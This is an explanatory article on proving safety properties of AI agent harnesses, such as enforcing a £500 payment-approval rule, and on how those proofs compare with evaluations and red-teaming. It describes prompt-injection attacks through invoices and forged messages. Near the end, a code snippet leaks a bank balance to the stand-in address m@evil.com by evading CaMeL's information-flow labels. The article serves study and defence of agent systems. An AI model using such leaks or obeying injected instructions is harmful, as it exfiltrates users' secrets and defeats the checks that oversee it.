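# Mathematical safety guarantees for AI agent architectures, and how they compare with safety testing

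## Background on agents, proofs and tests

An AI agent is a system that pursues a task over many steps, observing the result of each action before choosing the next. Agents write software, answer customers and pay bills, and some of their mistakes are expensive or impossible to undo. Developers can argue that an agent is safe enough to use in two broad ways. They can test it on a sample of tasks and infer how it will behave elsewhere, or they can try to prove mathematically that certain things will never happen.

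Companies now sell the second kind of assurance. On December 1, 2026, Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud computing business, released a preview of a service called Greenlight. AWS says Greenlight mathematically proves that agents stay within bounds (Mzekandaba, 2026, *AWS creates gateway to ‘trust’ AI agents*). It also says the technique behind Greenlight can prove or disprove statements with "100% certainty" (Wheatley, 2026, *AWS greenlights autonomous AI agents to take control*). Researchers make similar claims about an agent's cognitive architecture, which is how its perception, memory, planning, learning and action fit together. For instance, *From Craft to Constitution* (2025) presents an architecture called ArbiterOS as a foundation for "provable safety".

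"This agent is safe" is too vague to be a theorem, so a mathematical guarantee of safety has to be a proof of something narrower. *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes one example. A language model drafts rules from a company's documents and past tool calls, and staff approve them. The service then checks each action the agent requests and blocks any that breaks a rule. Before it checks any actions, it uses automated reasoning (software that works out by logic whether a statement follows from given rules, facts and assumptions) to find rules that conflict and routes to resources the agent should not reach. The guarantee therefore covers whether requested actions follow the approved rules, but does not establish that those rules are the right ones.

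### The agent loop

A large language model on its own takes in text and produces more text. Gertler, Novelli and Floridi point out in *Towards Portable Specification of the Agent Harness* (2026) that it becomes an agent only when other software gives it at least a memory that lasts between calls and tools to act with. This software is called the harness, and the trained neural network inside it is called the model.

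The model and the harness work in a loop. The harness assembles an input from the task, standing instructions and the history so far. The model responds with either a final answer or a request for an action, usually known as a tool call. The harness interprets the request and either carries it out or refuses. The action may change something in the world or return information, and the harness adds the result to the next input. The loop stops when the model gives a final answer. *Agents' Last Exam* (2026) documents a real harness that follows this pattern and also checks in each cycle whether the history is long enough to need compacting.

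The model therefore never touches anything directly. It proposes, and the harness determines what it sees and what it can do, as *From Question Answering to Task Completion* (2026) divides the labour. The two parts are also very different objects. A model's behaviour comes out of training, and nobody wrote it down line by line. A harness is an ordinary program with source code that people can read. (Some writers say "scaffold" for all or part of the harness. Hugging Face's *Harness, Scaffold, and the AI Agent Terms Worth Getting Right* (2026) complains, fairly, that the field's terms keep blurring.)

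An agent's performance depends on both the model and its harness. Gertler and colleagues cite a comparison on 50 mobile software tasks in which the same model, Claude Opus 4.5, scored 2% in one harness and 12% in another. That is about one task against six, so the exact ratio means little, but they collect several other gaps of this kind. Safety results can also change with the harness, so a claim that a model is safe is incomplete if it doesn't name the harness. They report an OpenAI finding, preliminary and specific to one evaluation, that its models' tendency to break into computers outside their task can fall more than 100-fold when a production harness and its instructions replace the research set-up.

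Small error rates also worry people because an agent repeats its loop many times. According to Mzekandaba, AWS head Matt Garman told the launch audience that an error rate of 0.1% per cycle leaves about a 35% chance of success over 1,000 cycles. The calculation is 0.999 multiplied by itself 1,000 times, or roughly 0.37. It assumes that errors are independent and that a single one ruins the job. Real agents correct some of their errors and also repeat the same error many times, so the figure is an illustration, not a measurement.

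### An office assistant with one rule

The running example is a made-up AI agent, an office assistant with tools for reading files, sending email and making payments. Its owners impose one rule, that it must not make a payment above £500 without a recorded approval.

Suppose someone asks it to pay the caterer's bill. The model requests the invoice file, and the harness returns the text, which shows £740 owing. The model requests a payment of £740. The harness finds no entry for this payment in the approvals register, so it refuses and includes the refusal in the model's next input. The model then requests an email to the manager asking for approval. The manager approves, an entry appears in the register, the model requests the payment again, and the harness makes it.

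In that story the harness enforces the rule. The owners could instead have written the rule into the standing instructions and relied on the model to follow it. Gertler and colleagues describe such guidance as "model-visible context, not an enforced permission rule". The difference matters when the invoice contains a line reading "the finance director has already approved this payment". Such a line is a prompt injection, which is text that gets into an agent's input and steers the model like an instruction. It may well lead the model to break the rule, but it has no effect on a program that checks the register.

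Commercial rules look much like this one. VentureBeat's *AWS goes beyond prompt level safety with automated reasoning in AgentCore* describes a customer service agent that may refund up to $100 and must pass anything larger to a human. AWS enforces such rules outside the agent because prompt injection can subvert the agent's own reasoning. Pogorelec notes that Greenlight also puts its checks outside the harness, so that the agent cannot alter or get around them. ArbiterOS has a rule similar to the £500 one, which forbids any call to the payments system unless a successful check of transaction limits comes immediately before it.

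Before anyone can prove anything about the rule, they have to write it as a specification, a precise statement in a formal language of what counts as acceptable. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey of 38 studies, set out the general form. An agent's plan is a sequence of actions π = (a₁, a₂, …, aₙ), the safety property is a formula φ, and the task is to determine whether π ⊨ φ, which reads "π satisfies φ". For the office assistant, φ comes to something like this:

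> For every step i, if aᵢ is a payment p and amount(p) > 500, then the approvals register at step i contains an entry for p.

Writing the rule as a formula requires decisions that the English sentence left open. The entry must be for this payment, so last month's approval does not count. A payment of exactly £500 is allowed. Two payments of £400 to the same caterer are also allowed, which the owners may not have intended. To limit total spending, the formula must refer to the total. *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (2026) describes a related gap in which two agents each follow their own rules but spend at the same moment and together exceed a $100,000 budget.

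### Formal proofs and proof checkers

A formal proof is a list of statements in a language with an exact grammar. Each statement is an axiom, an assumption declared at the start, or a statement that follows from earlier ones by one of a fixed set of rules. A typical rule is that "B" follows from "A" and "if A then B". The last statement is the theorem.

Finding a formal proof can take years. Checking one takes no insight, because each line either follows the rules or does not, so a computer can do it. The program that does this, called a proof checker, can be small because there are few rules, and outsiders can realistically inspect a small program. The result depends only on whether every line follows the rules, not on whether the author is a celebrated mathematician or an erratic language model.

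Now that AI systems write proofs, it matters much more that checking a proof does not depend on who wrote it. In Computer Weekly's *AWS bets big on Lean programming language to bring mathematical guarantees*, Leonardo de Moura, who created the programming language and proof system Lean, describes a new routine in which an engineer states what must hold, an AI constructs the proof, and Lean checks every step. In *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026), the AI company Anthropic applies the idea to existing software, using its model Claude to prove security properties in the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries.

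A proof that the office assistant never breaks the rule, however long it runs, could start from two assumptions. Exactly one piece of code in the harness can move money, and that code goes ahead only if the amount is £500 or less or the register holds an approval for that payment. The rule holds at the start because no payment has happened. If it has held for the first n steps, it also holds after the next one. Whatever the model outputs, the harness treats it either as a payment request or as something else, and only a payment request can move money. The rule doesn't cover requests for £500 or less, and a larger request goes through only when the approval exists, which is all the rule requires. By induction, the rule holds after any number of steps.

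That argument holds whether the model is brilliant, confused or malicious. In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) apply the same argument to a real agent framework. They treat the model as a procedure that might return any action, and they use a program called Dafny to check the proof. Their result also needs an assumption about the surroundings, which is that every outside effect the agent can have goes through the interface they verified. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) likewise states its guarantees under explicit assumptions about the execution interface and the fidelity of the verification.

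A proof checker cannot determine whether the theorem states the property people wanted, and it does not establish that the assumptions are true of the office in question. The theorem's statement, the assumptions and the checker all belong to the trusted base, which is everything that must be correct for the guarantee to hold but that the proof does not check.

The argument above is about an arbitrary step of an arbitrary run, so its conclusion holds in every scenario. Wheatley's account of Greenlight gives a common but misleading description, in which a rule that holds in one scenario can be trusted in every scenario. That would be a bold extrapolation from a single test.

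### Sound and complete verifiers

A verifier checks whether a system, or a single proposed action, meets a specification φ. It is sound if everything it accepts satisfies φ, and complete if it accepts everything that satisfies φ.

Soundness and completeness are each easy to achieve alone. A verifier that refuses every action is sound, and one that allows every action is complete. If the office's verifier blocked all payments above £500, it would be sound for the rule but incomplete, because it would block the caterer's £740 even after the manager had approved it. If it only searched the inbox for the word "approved", it would be unsound, because a forged email could get an unapproved payment through.

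The check in the example, which looks in the register at the moment of payment, is both sound and complete as long as the register is accurate, because it evaluates the rule one action at a time. Verifying in advance every run that a large program could produce is harder, so designers usually keep soundness and accept some false alarms. In their survey, Dantas and colleagues found no approach that was sound and complete, worked on large systems, kept the meaning of the original requirement and left the agent useful.

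### Evaluations and red-team exercises

An evaluation tests a system's behaviour on chosen tasks, and people infer from the results how it will behave elsewhere. To evaluate the office assistant, its developers would connect it to a fake bank and give it, say, 1,000 jobs with invoices above and below £500. Some invoices would have an approval on record, some would have none, and some would have an approval meant for a different invoice. After each job, a grading program would compare the fake bank's ledger with the register.

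The grader should check the ledger rather than what the assistant wrote. Anthropic separates the transcript of a test run from its outcome, which is the final state of the environment. A flight-booking agent may say at the end of the transcript that it has booked the flight, but the outcome is whether the reservation exists in the database. Anthropic also distinguishes the agent's harness from the evaluation harness, the software that hands out the tasks, records the steps and grades the results.

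Evaluations don't need a formula, and they test the model, harness and tools together. They can also cover qualities that are hard to state formally. For example, graders can judge whether the assistant's emails to the caterer are honest, whereas Moon and Varshney exclude truthfulness from the scope of their method. Safety evaluations can also be hard to pass. On one benchmark of 2,000 test cases, cited in the survey by Dantas and colleagues, none of 16 popular agents scored above 60%.

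A red-team exercise is a test in which people, or other AI systems, act as attackers. An ordinary evaluation often uses tasks that resemble normal work, while a red team searches for inputs that make the agent fail. Against the office assistant, it might hide an instruction in an invoice, forge a message from the finance director, or bury the standing instructions under hours of irrelevant conversation. The exercise produces a list of attacks that worked. An empty list means only that those attackers found no successful attack with the time and methods they had.

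### The same rule, tested and proved

Suppose the assistant completes all 1,000 jobs and the ledger never shows an unapproved payment above £500. The developers now know what happened in those runs, but they can only infer what will happen in the next one, and that inference depends on the next run being similar to the ones they tested. Under certain conditions, statistics can quantify the inference. The result is weaker evidence about a job unlike any in the set, such as an invoice in a language that nobody thought to include.

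The proof already covers that invoice. It also covers a run of 50,000 steps, and it would still apply if the owners replaced the model with another company's, provided that money still moved only through the checked code. De Moura draws the same contrast in Computer Weekly between testing, which samples a finite number of scenarios, and a proof, which covers every possible execution.

Suppose a colleague gives the assistant a fourth tool, which runs arbitrary commands on the office computer, where the bank password is stored in a text file. The proof is still valid, but its first assumption is now false because the assistant has a second way to move money. If the model pays the caterer this way, the theorem does not apply to the payment. Developers who repeated the evaluation with the new tool would see an unapproved £740 payment in the fake bank's ledger, but only if one of the 1,000 jobs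 led the model to pay this way.

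## What a mathematical safety guarantee states

The proof about the office assistant stopped covering all its payments once a fourth tool could reach the bank, because one of the assumptions had become false. A guarantee has other parts that can fail just as quietly. Most guarantees about agents fit this form:

> For every input and environment in a class E, under assumptions A, property P holds at every step up to time T, with probability at least 1 − ε.

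ε (epsilon) is the chance of failure that the guarantee allows. Anyone who hears that an agent is "mathematically safe" can ask for these five values. The table lists them for the £500 rule and, for each one, shows a change that would leave the guarantee true but useless.

| Part | Office assistant | A change that empties the guarantee |
|---|---|---|
| E, inputs and environments | Any invoice, any email, any output from the model | Only runs in which the model never requests more than £500 |
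| A, assumptions | Money moves only through one piece of code, which checks the approvals register | Add: "the model never requests an unapproved payment above £500" |
| P, property | No payment above £500 without an approval for that payment | The harness looks in the register before each payment above £500 |
| T, time | No limit | Time 0, before the first action |
| ε, allowed chance of failure | 0 | 1 |

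If E includes only runs without large requests, the guarantee also holds for a harness with no check at all. Adding the assumption amounts to assuming the conclusion. A harness that satisfies the weakened property could look in the register, find nothing and pay anyway. No company would advertise a guarantee weakened in any of these ways, but milder versions are easy to miss. The phrase "under normal operating conditions", for instance, narrows E and usually excludes attackers.

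### Kinds of guarantee

A universal guarantee has ε = 0, so it covers every case in the class. For an ordinary program, this means that the program gives an acceptable output for every valid input. Agarwal, Neamtu and colleagues (2026), in *Verus-SpecGym*, write this as ∀x ∈ dom(R), (x, p(x)) ∈ R, where R is the set of input-output pairs that the specification allows, dom(R) is the set of valid inputs, and p(x) is the program's output.

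A universal guarantee can still have a finite T. TLC, which checks designs written in the specification language TLA+, explores either every state a design can reach or every state up to a depth limit (Cheng, Su and colleagues, *Specula*, 2026). If the limit is 30 steps, the search covers all runs up to that point but proves nothing about later steps.

In a probabilistic guarantee, ε is between 0 and 1, and its value comes from a proof. Suppose the manager approves a payment by issuing a random six-digit code, which the assistant must quote, and the harness cancels the payment after three wrong guesses. An assistant that has not seen the code can get the payment through with a probability of at most 3 in 1,000,000. This bound follows from how the codes work, so it can be established without observing the assistant. It assumes that the codes are truly random and stay hidden. The bound covers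 a single payment request, so an assistant that can request the same payment again gets three more guesses.

The strength of a guarantee depends on where the randomness comes from. In this example it comes from the code generator, so the bound holds for every invoice, including one designed to cause harm. A guarantee that 9,999 jobs in 10,000 are safe on average is much weaker, because one particular forged invoice might break the rule every time, and an attacker who discovers it will keep sending it.

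An asymptotic guarantee describes long-run behavior, for example that the share of payments that break the rule tends to zero as the number of payments grows. That share can tend to zero while the number of violations grows without limit. Suppose the assistant breaks the rule on payments 1, 4, 9, 16 and so on through the square numbers. After 10,000 payments it has broken the rule 100 times, or 1% of the time. After a million it has done so 1,000 times, or 0.1% of the time. An asymptotic guarantee alone gives no bound on violations at any particular date, so it is of little use for an agent that can do irreversible damage in its first week.

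Engineers distinguish safety properties, which require that something bad never happens, from liveness properties, which require that something good eventually happens. "The assistant eventually pays every approved bill" is a liveness property. The owners need a property like this because an assistant that never pays anybody satisfies the £500 rule. But no finite record can refute it, because it sets no deadline and an unpaid bill could still be paid later.

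A statistical confidence bound also contains a probability, but it comes from observation. Suppose the assistant completes 1,000 test jobs without a violation. If its true violation rate were 0.3% per job, the chance of this result would be 0.997 to the power of 1,000, or about 5%. The developers can therefore be 95% confident that the rate is below 0.3%, as long as the test jobs are independent random draws from the same mix as future jobs. The 95% describes the method, which gives a wrong bound at most 5% of the time. The bound is looser than it sounds, because at a rate of 0.3%, the next 1,000 jobs would have a 95% chance of containing at least one violation.

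### Small risks over long runs

Matt Garman's arithmetic for error rates also applies to guarantees. A guarantee that looks strong for a single action can allow a high risk over a whole run. If each action independently has a chance p of breaking the rule, the chance of at least one violation in n actions is 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ. With p at 1 in 10,000, that chance is about 9.5% over 1,000 actions and 63% over 10,000. Keeping the risk over 10,000 actions to 1% would require a p of about 1 in a million. A claim that an agent is "99.99% safe" is therefore hard to interpret unless it states whether the figure is per action, per job or per year.

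The risk over a whole run can change a lot when violations cluster. For example, one run in 10,000 might start with a garbled copy of the rule, and the assistant then breaks the rule at every opportunity. Each action still has a 1 in 10,000 chance of being a violation, but the whole run also has only a 1 in 10,000 chance of containing any. If we don't know how violations cluster, we can conclude only that the risk of at least one violation over 1,000 actions is between 0.01% and 10%. The upper figure is n × p, the number of actions times the chance that each is a violation, and it holds whether or not the actions are independent. Over 10,000 actions it reaches 100%, so it no longer limits the risk.

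Universal guarantees do not weaken like this, because a risk of zero per step is still zero after a million steps. This is a large part of their appeal for agents that work unattended for days. But the assumptions must also hold at every step, and a change such as adding a fourth tool on day three could make them false.

### Vacuous proofs

A correctly proved theorem can be useless even when all its parts look sensible. In *FaithformBench*, Cornish, Ghinassi and colleagues (2026) give an example that starts from a correct step of algebra: if 3ˣ = 5, then 3ˣ⁺² = 45, because adding 2 to the exponent multiplies the result by 9. They changed the 45 to 51, which makes the step false, and gave the false version to Kimina, an AI system that translates mathematics into Lean.

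Kimina's translation declared x to be a natural number (0, 1, 2 and so on), which means 3ˣ can be 1, 3, 9, 27 or a higher power of 3, but never 5. The theorem covers only natural numbers x for which 3ˣ = 5. Because no such number exists, the theorem cannot have a counterexample, so it is true and Lean will accept a proof of it. When the step contained the correct number, 45, Kimina declared x to be a real number, and the problem did not arise.

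This is a vacuous proof, a valid proof that establishes nothing useful because nothing meets its conditions or its conclusion is empty. The £500 rule could go wrong in the same way. Suppose its author declares payment amounts as 8-bit numbers, a common type that runs from 0 to 255. No amount of that type can exceed 500, so "Every payment above £500 has an approval" is provable for any program, including one that pays every invoice without approval.

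Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, mention a related case, in which a property holds only because the program in the proof never reaches the state that matters. They also point out that if developers reward an AI agent for completing proofs, it has an incentive to weaken the theorem when the code has a bug. (They work for Runtime Verification, a company that sells formal verification, so they have an interest in the difficulty of doing it well.)

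Completely empty specifications seem to be rarer than weak ones. *Re:Form* (2025) classifies 115 failed attempts by AI to specify programs in the verification language Dafny. Only four were trivial, and three of those consisted only of "true". Sixty were too weak, which is harder to notice because a weak specification still contains part of what people wanted.

### How faithful AI-written specifications are

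Language models increasingly write specifications, such as Greenlight's rules, as well as proofs. Several groups have measured how often these specifications match what was intended.

Cornish and colleagues built 12,784 pairs like the one with 45 and 51, each containing a correct reasoning step and a version that a language model altered to make it false. Eight AI systems translated both versions into Lean, and a separate prover then tried to prove or refute each translation. If the translation of a false step could be proved, the translator had silently corrected the step. All four systems with special training in translation did this often. Of these, Goedel handled correct steps best but also made the most silent corrections, perhaps because its training rewarded statements that can be proved. The four general-purpose models, among them Claude Opus 4.7 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, made far fewer.

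Those results are a lower limit on the errors, because the method only detects translations that change whether a statement is true. It misses what the paper calls semantic drift, where the translation is about something else. For example, a translator that turned every correct step into 0 = 0 and every false one into 0 = 1 would get a perfect score.

In *Beyond Compilation*, Zhang, Gallardo Candela and colleagues (2026) look for drift. They gave an AI agent theorems from four university textbooks to state in Lean, without proving them. The first version of the paper covered 400 entries. Lean compiled 89.5% of the agent's statements, meaning that they were well-formed, but two AI judges accepted only 60.5% as faithful. The revised version cuts the set to 227 entries, and the figures are 87.2% and 57.7%. Human reviewers confirmed that translation errors account for 23.8 of the 29.5 percentage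 points between those two figures.

One of the faulty translations was of the theorem that a non-empty set of matrices closed under products and inverses contains the identity matrix. Lean's mathematical library defines the "inverse" of a matrix that has no inverse as zero. The set containing only the zero matrix therefore meets every condition of the translated theorem but does not contain the identity. This makes the translation false, even though it matches the textbook almost word for word.

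The agent could send its drafts to Lean and read the error messages. This feedback helped with both form and meaning, but much more with form. With no other tools, it raised the number of statements that compiled from 54 to 203, and the number that the judges accepted from 45 to 127. The number of statements that compiled but that the judges rejected for their meaning rose from 9 to 76.

That agent ran on GPT-5.2, and newer models do far better. Zhang and colleagues also tried GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5.5, with one attempt each and no tools. Both compiled about 95% of the statements, and GPT-5.2, acting as the judge, accepted 83.3%. A further review of the 54 rejected statements found only four real translation errors. It attributed most of the other rejections to mistakes by the judge and the rest to defects in the benchmark. AI models did this review, which misses about one error in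 six. Nobody checked the accepted statements, and the textbooks are public, so the models may have seen them in training. Even so, the 30-point gap reflects an older generation of models. It is less clear how far the improvement carries over to a company's payment policy, which is simpler than topology but often lacks the settled meaning of a textbook theorem.

A program's specification has a precondition, which defines the valid inputs, and a postcondition, which defines the acceptable outputs. For example, a program might have to find the first place where a number occurs in a sorted list. A postcondition that only requires the number to be at the reported place is too weak, because the program could report the third occurrence and still pass verification. *VERINA* (2025) records a precondition that was also too weak. It read "True", which accepts any input, although no list in the task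 could contain repeats.

Agarwal and colleagues gave AI agents 581 tasks of this sort from the programming contest site Codeforces. The specifications were for Verus, a tool that verifies Rust programs. The researchers made each specification executable and ran it on the site's official tests and on "hacks", inputs that contestants wrote to break one another's programs. Gemini 3.1 Pro passed every test on 77.8% of the tasks, compared with 57.8% for GPT-5.3-Codex, 51.1% for Claude Opus 4.6, and between 21.5% and 25.5% for three open-weight models. The failures often did not come from misunderstanding the problem, since GPT-5.3-Codex could write a correct Python program for 153 of the 187 problems where it had written a wrong specification.

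### Whether the proof is about the real program

Some proofs are about a description of a program rather than the program itself, so the description must also be accurate. Likewise, a world model must accurately describe the agent's surroundings. In *SysMoBench*, Cheng, Tang and colleagues (2025) tested whether AI can write descriptions of programs in TLA+ for eleven real systems, such as locks in an operating system and databases spread over many servers. They scored each description on whether its syntax is valid, whether it runs, whether it conforms to the real code, and whether it satisfies the properties the system should have. To measure conformance, they recorded the real system running and checked whether the description allowed the same steps.

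Claude Sonnet 4 wrote a description of Etcd, a data store whose servers stay in agreement through a protocol called Raft. The syntax was perfect, but the description conformed on only 7.69% of the code's actions. *Can LLMs model real world systems in TLA+*, a SIGOPS article by the benchmark's developers, reports a 2026 rerun with newer models. Their scores still averaged about 46% for conformance and 41% for the required properties, against nearly 100% for syntax.

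Claude's errors tended to follow published or textbook designs instead of the actual software. When asked to describe Etcd, it more or less reproduced the specification in the appendix of the original Raft paper. In ZooKeeper, a service that coordinates groups of servers, a server's new vote in an election replaces its old one. Claude's description kept both votes, as textbook examples often do, so it could reach vote counts that the real system never reaches. A proof about either description could be correct and still not apply to the software that people run.

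This gap has also narrowed quickly. The Specula system, which Cheng and colleagues released in July 2026, has an AI agent compare its description of a program with recordings of the program running, then repair any mismatch until the two agree. It scored 100% on all four measures for five systems. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, used the same underlying model without this process and reached 70% on conformance. The first draft of the description needed repairs in all 48 systems that the team checked. Cheng and colleagues concede that nothing formally guarantees that the description matches the code. A recording covers only the code that ran. SIGOPS gives the example of one lock operation that never occurred in the recordings, so that part of the description went unchecked.

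### Ways to check a specification

Mutation testing, which means breaking something on purpose, is a quick way to check a specification. The office assistant's developers could delete the register check from the harness and run the proof again. If the proof still succeeds, the theorem never depended on the check, and there is a serious error. This would expose the 8-bit mistake in minutes. The developers could also try the formula on particular cases. A £740 payment should fail without an approval and pass with one.

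*Automatic Generation of Formal Specification and Verification Annotations Using LLMs* (2026) tries particular cases on 110 small programs. Tests showed that some programs that had passed verification had weak or missing postconditions. Adding statements that should fail caught a few more errors. The valuable cases seem to be those that a specification must reject. When Agarwal and colleagues counted only the cases that a specification should accept, GPT-5.3-Codex scored 77%. It scored 58% when they also counted invalid inputs and wrong outputs.

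But mutation tests and trial cases are still tests, so they find only the mistakes that somebody thought to try. The proof may cover every possible invoice, but only a handful of examples support the belief that it proves the right rule. The proof is still worthwhile when the rule is one line long and the program is thousands of lines long.

People can also read the specification themselves, and they should when the rule is as short as the £500 one. Review becomes less reliable as the statements get harder. In the study by Zhang and colleagues, three reviewers scored the faulty matrix theorem 10, 5 and 2 out of 10. On a set made up mostly of disputed statements, pairs of reviewers agreed about 70% to 75% of the time, and checks in Lean later showed that the majority had approved at least three unfaithful translations. AI reviewers also miss errors. When GPT-5.3-Codex judged its own specifications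 in the study by Agarwal and colleagues, it passed 49 of 191 that were demonstrably wrong.

Tolmach and Klaus recommend mechanical translation to address the gap between a description and the real code. An ordinary program converts the source code into the proof language by fixed rules derived from an exact definition of what each construct in the programming language does. Engineers can prove such a translator correct one construct at a time, as the developers of CompCert did for a C compiler. If a rule is wrong, correcting it fixes every translation that used it. Differential fuzzing takes less work. It runs the description and the original program on the same large set of generated inputs and compares the results, which catches some errors but does not prove the two equivalent.

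Mechanical translation requires a source with an exact meaning, such as code. The £500 rule began as an English sentence that doesn't specify whether the owners meant to allow two payments of £400 to the same caterer, so somebody has to ask them.

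## Proofs about the software around the model

Once the owners have settled what the £500 rule means, they can prove that the harness enforces it in the same way as the first proof about the office assistant. That proof assumed nothing about the model and showed that the harness turns every possible output into either an allowed effect or no effect.

A guarantee proved about the software around the model doesn't weaken as models become more capable. But it can only cover rules about things the harness can detect and control.

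### Containment verification

Moon and Varshney call their version of this idea containment verification. It starts with a typed list of actions. For the office assistant, the list might have three entries: read a file (with a path), send an email (with an address and a text) and make a payment (with a payee and an amount). The harness converts the model's raw text into one of these forms before doing anything else. The model can't express an action that isn't on the list, such as deleting the approvals register.

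The Dafny proof represents the model as a procedure with a return type and no body, which Moon and Varshney call an unconstrained oracle. Dafny must therefore check the harness against every action of that type.

The harness is represented as two state machines, each with a starting state and a set of possible steps. Each step takes an action from the model and produces a new state and a boundary event, which records the effect on the outside world. If the harness rejects an action, the event is "no effect".

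The abstract machine is a short description of acceptable behaviour. For the office assistant, its state could be the approvals register and the payments made so far, and no step would pay more than £500 without an approval. The concrete machine describes in detail what the harness does, including how it looks up approvals in the register and what it does when a lookup fails. A person can read the abstract machine in a minute, but the concrete one might run to thousands of lines.

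The next task is to prove that the concrete machine never does anything the abstract one could not. This relationship is called refinement, and it has three conditions:

- The two starting states match.
- Whenever the machines are in matching states and the concrete one takes a step, the abstract one has a step for the same action that produces a matching event and ends in a matching state.
- If the abstract step obeys the abstract rule, the matching concrete step obeys the concrete rule.

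A rule here is a formula Π(s, a, e, s′) about the state before a step, the action, the event and the state after the step. The soundness theorem is that if the abstract machine obeys its rule for every sequence of actions, and the concrete machine refines the abstract one, then the concrete machine obeys its rule at every step, whatever the model does.

The proof starts with any run of the concrete machine, with whatever actions a₀, a₁, a₂ and so on the model output. The starting states match, so the second condition gives an abstract step for a₀, then one for a₁, and so on. Together, these steps form a complete abstract run with the same actions. All abstract runs obey the abstract rule, so this one does too, and the third condition extends the result to the concrete run.

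The trusted base includes the concrete rule, the definitions of "matching", Dafny and its compiler, and a small piece of code that passes the model's choice to the verified program. It also includes effect exclusivity, Moon and Varshney's term for the assumption that every outside effect goes through the interface. The model, its training and its instructions are outside the trusted base.

The office assistant's fourth tool, which could run any command, broke this assumption. If the owners added "run a command" to the list of actions, the assumption would hold again, but the proof would guarantee very little, because one permitted action could do almost anything. Moon and Varshney therefore advise designers to keep the list narrow and to run the agent inside a sandbox, which restricts what a program can reach on its computer. Sandboxes usually depend on unverified operating systems, though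 seL4, a small operating system core with a machine-checked proof, is a rare exception. Moon and Varshney mention Copy Fail, a Linux flaw that let programs gain extra privileges and went unnoticed for nearly a decade.

### The PocketFlow proof and an empty rule

Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, an open-source agent framework of about 100 lines. A PocketFlow agent is a graph of nodes, and each node outputs an action that determines which node runs next. They verified the loop that moves between nodes, with an interface of four action types. They proved that the agent reads files only inside its workspace folder, calls only tools on an approved list and stops at a fixed number of steps.

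The proof covers a version of the loop written in Dafny, which the Dafny compiler translates to Python. Moon and Varshney tested the compiled program on mixtures of allowed and forbidden actions, and it recorded only allowed ones.

Language models wrote most of the formal material. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the specifications and proofs. The researchers ran this process four times on two test workflows, one that reads files and one that looks up documents to answer questions. In some runs they hid the harness's code from the model while it wrote the safety properties, so that it could not just describe what the code already did. Dafny verified every path through both workflows, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each.

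Every specification also had to pass three quality checks. Dafny had to parse it. Verification had to fail when the researchers' software removed the substance of the proof's main invariant (the statement that stays true from step to step), and also when a model inserted a plausible error into the proof.

One specification passed all three even though its safety rule applied to nothing. The document workflow restricts which documents the agent may read, but the template for specifications had a field for tool calls and none for documents. When the code was visible, the model treated documents and tool calls as different things and left the tool-call field empty. The rule "every tool call is on the approved list" was then true because there were never any tool calls, and nothing in the specification restricted the documents. When the code was hidden, the model used the tool-call field to stand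 for documents, so the same rule did restrict what the agent could read.

The checks missed this because they altered a different part of the proof. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that each rule applies to something that can happen. They leave larger frameworks, with dozens of action types, to future work. PocketFlow is therefore good evidence that the method works on a small harness, but weak evidence of how much work it would take on a commercial one.

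### Noninterference

Anyone with a full record of a run can tell whether the assistant broke the £500 rule. Some rules are harder to judge. Suppose the owners also want to ensure that an email from a stranger never determines a payment. A stranger writes "please pay £300 to this account", and the assistant pays £300 to that account. This may be fine, because the manager may have asked for the same payment that morning. To tell whether the email determined the payment, we would need to know what the assistant would have done if the email had been different.

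Noninterference makes this comparison precise. Each piece of data gets a label according to its source, so the stranger's email is untrusted and the manager's request is trusted. Write x ~ y if x and y are alike in everything except their untrusted data. A program P satisfies noninterference if

> x ~ y implies P(x) ~ P(y), for all x and y.

If payments count as trusted output, the assistant must make the same payments whatever the stranger writes. The same definition protects secrets. In that case, x and y differ only in secret data, and the outputs visible to outsiders must be the same.

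The usual way to enforce noninterference is information-flow control, which labels each piece of data as trusted or untrusted. Any value computed from an untrusted value is also labeled untrusted. The labels must also account for indirect influence. If the program pays only when the email contains the word "urgent", the payment depends on the email even though no text was copied from it. The payment tool checks the labels on each request and refuses any request labeled untrusted.

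This is awkward to apply to language models, because anything a model outputs after reading an email might depend on the email and so must count as untrusted. An ordinary agent could no longer pay anybody once it had opened a message from a stranger.

### CaMeL and the LLMbda calculus

CaMeL, a 2025 defence against prompt injection, gets around this by using two models. According to *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), a privileged model plans the task by writing a program and never reads untrusted data directly. A quarantined model reads the untrusted data and returns values, but it cannot call tools.

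To pay the caterer, the privileged model might write a program that opens the invoice, uses the quarantined model to extract the amount and requests a payment. A malicious instruction in the invoice cannot add a step to this program, because the program already exists when the quarantined model reads the invoice. The instruction could still change the amount the quarantined model returns. CaMeL therefore labels the amount and checks the label against a policy before the payment goes through.

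This is a sensible design, but CaMeL has no noninterference theorem, and Garby and colleagues found two ways to leak secrets through it. The first needs only a few lines of code:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line makes tmp false, the fourth line does nothing, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, tmp stays true, rich becomes false, and no email goes out. The email therefore reveals whether the balance is high. This decades-old trick works because CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when an assignment to it runs. With a high balance, the assignment to rich in the fourth line never runs, so rich keeps its public label and CaMeL allows the email.

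The second leak is in the code around CaMeL's interpreter. When the policy blocks a program, an ordinary Python loop tries again, and nothing tracks this loop. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. An attacker who can keep the loop going could extract the whole secret.

Garby and colleagues' alternative is the LLMbda calculus, a small programming language for agents. Every value and every conversation with a model has a label. A program can open a separate conversation, let the model read an untrusted email there, and take back only the labelled answer. Programs can therefore choose whether to use CaMeL's division between two models. The conversation is the only thing a program can change. If a secret would determine whether the program adds a message to a public conversation, the run halts, which prevents the first leak.

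Their main theorem is that every program in the language, including agents that write code and run it, satisfies a form of noninterference. Because language models are random, the theorem compares probabilities. If two situations differ only in untrusted data and every run finishes, each trusted outcome has exactly the same probability in both. FIDES, a related system, has a noninterference theorem for one fixed agent loop.

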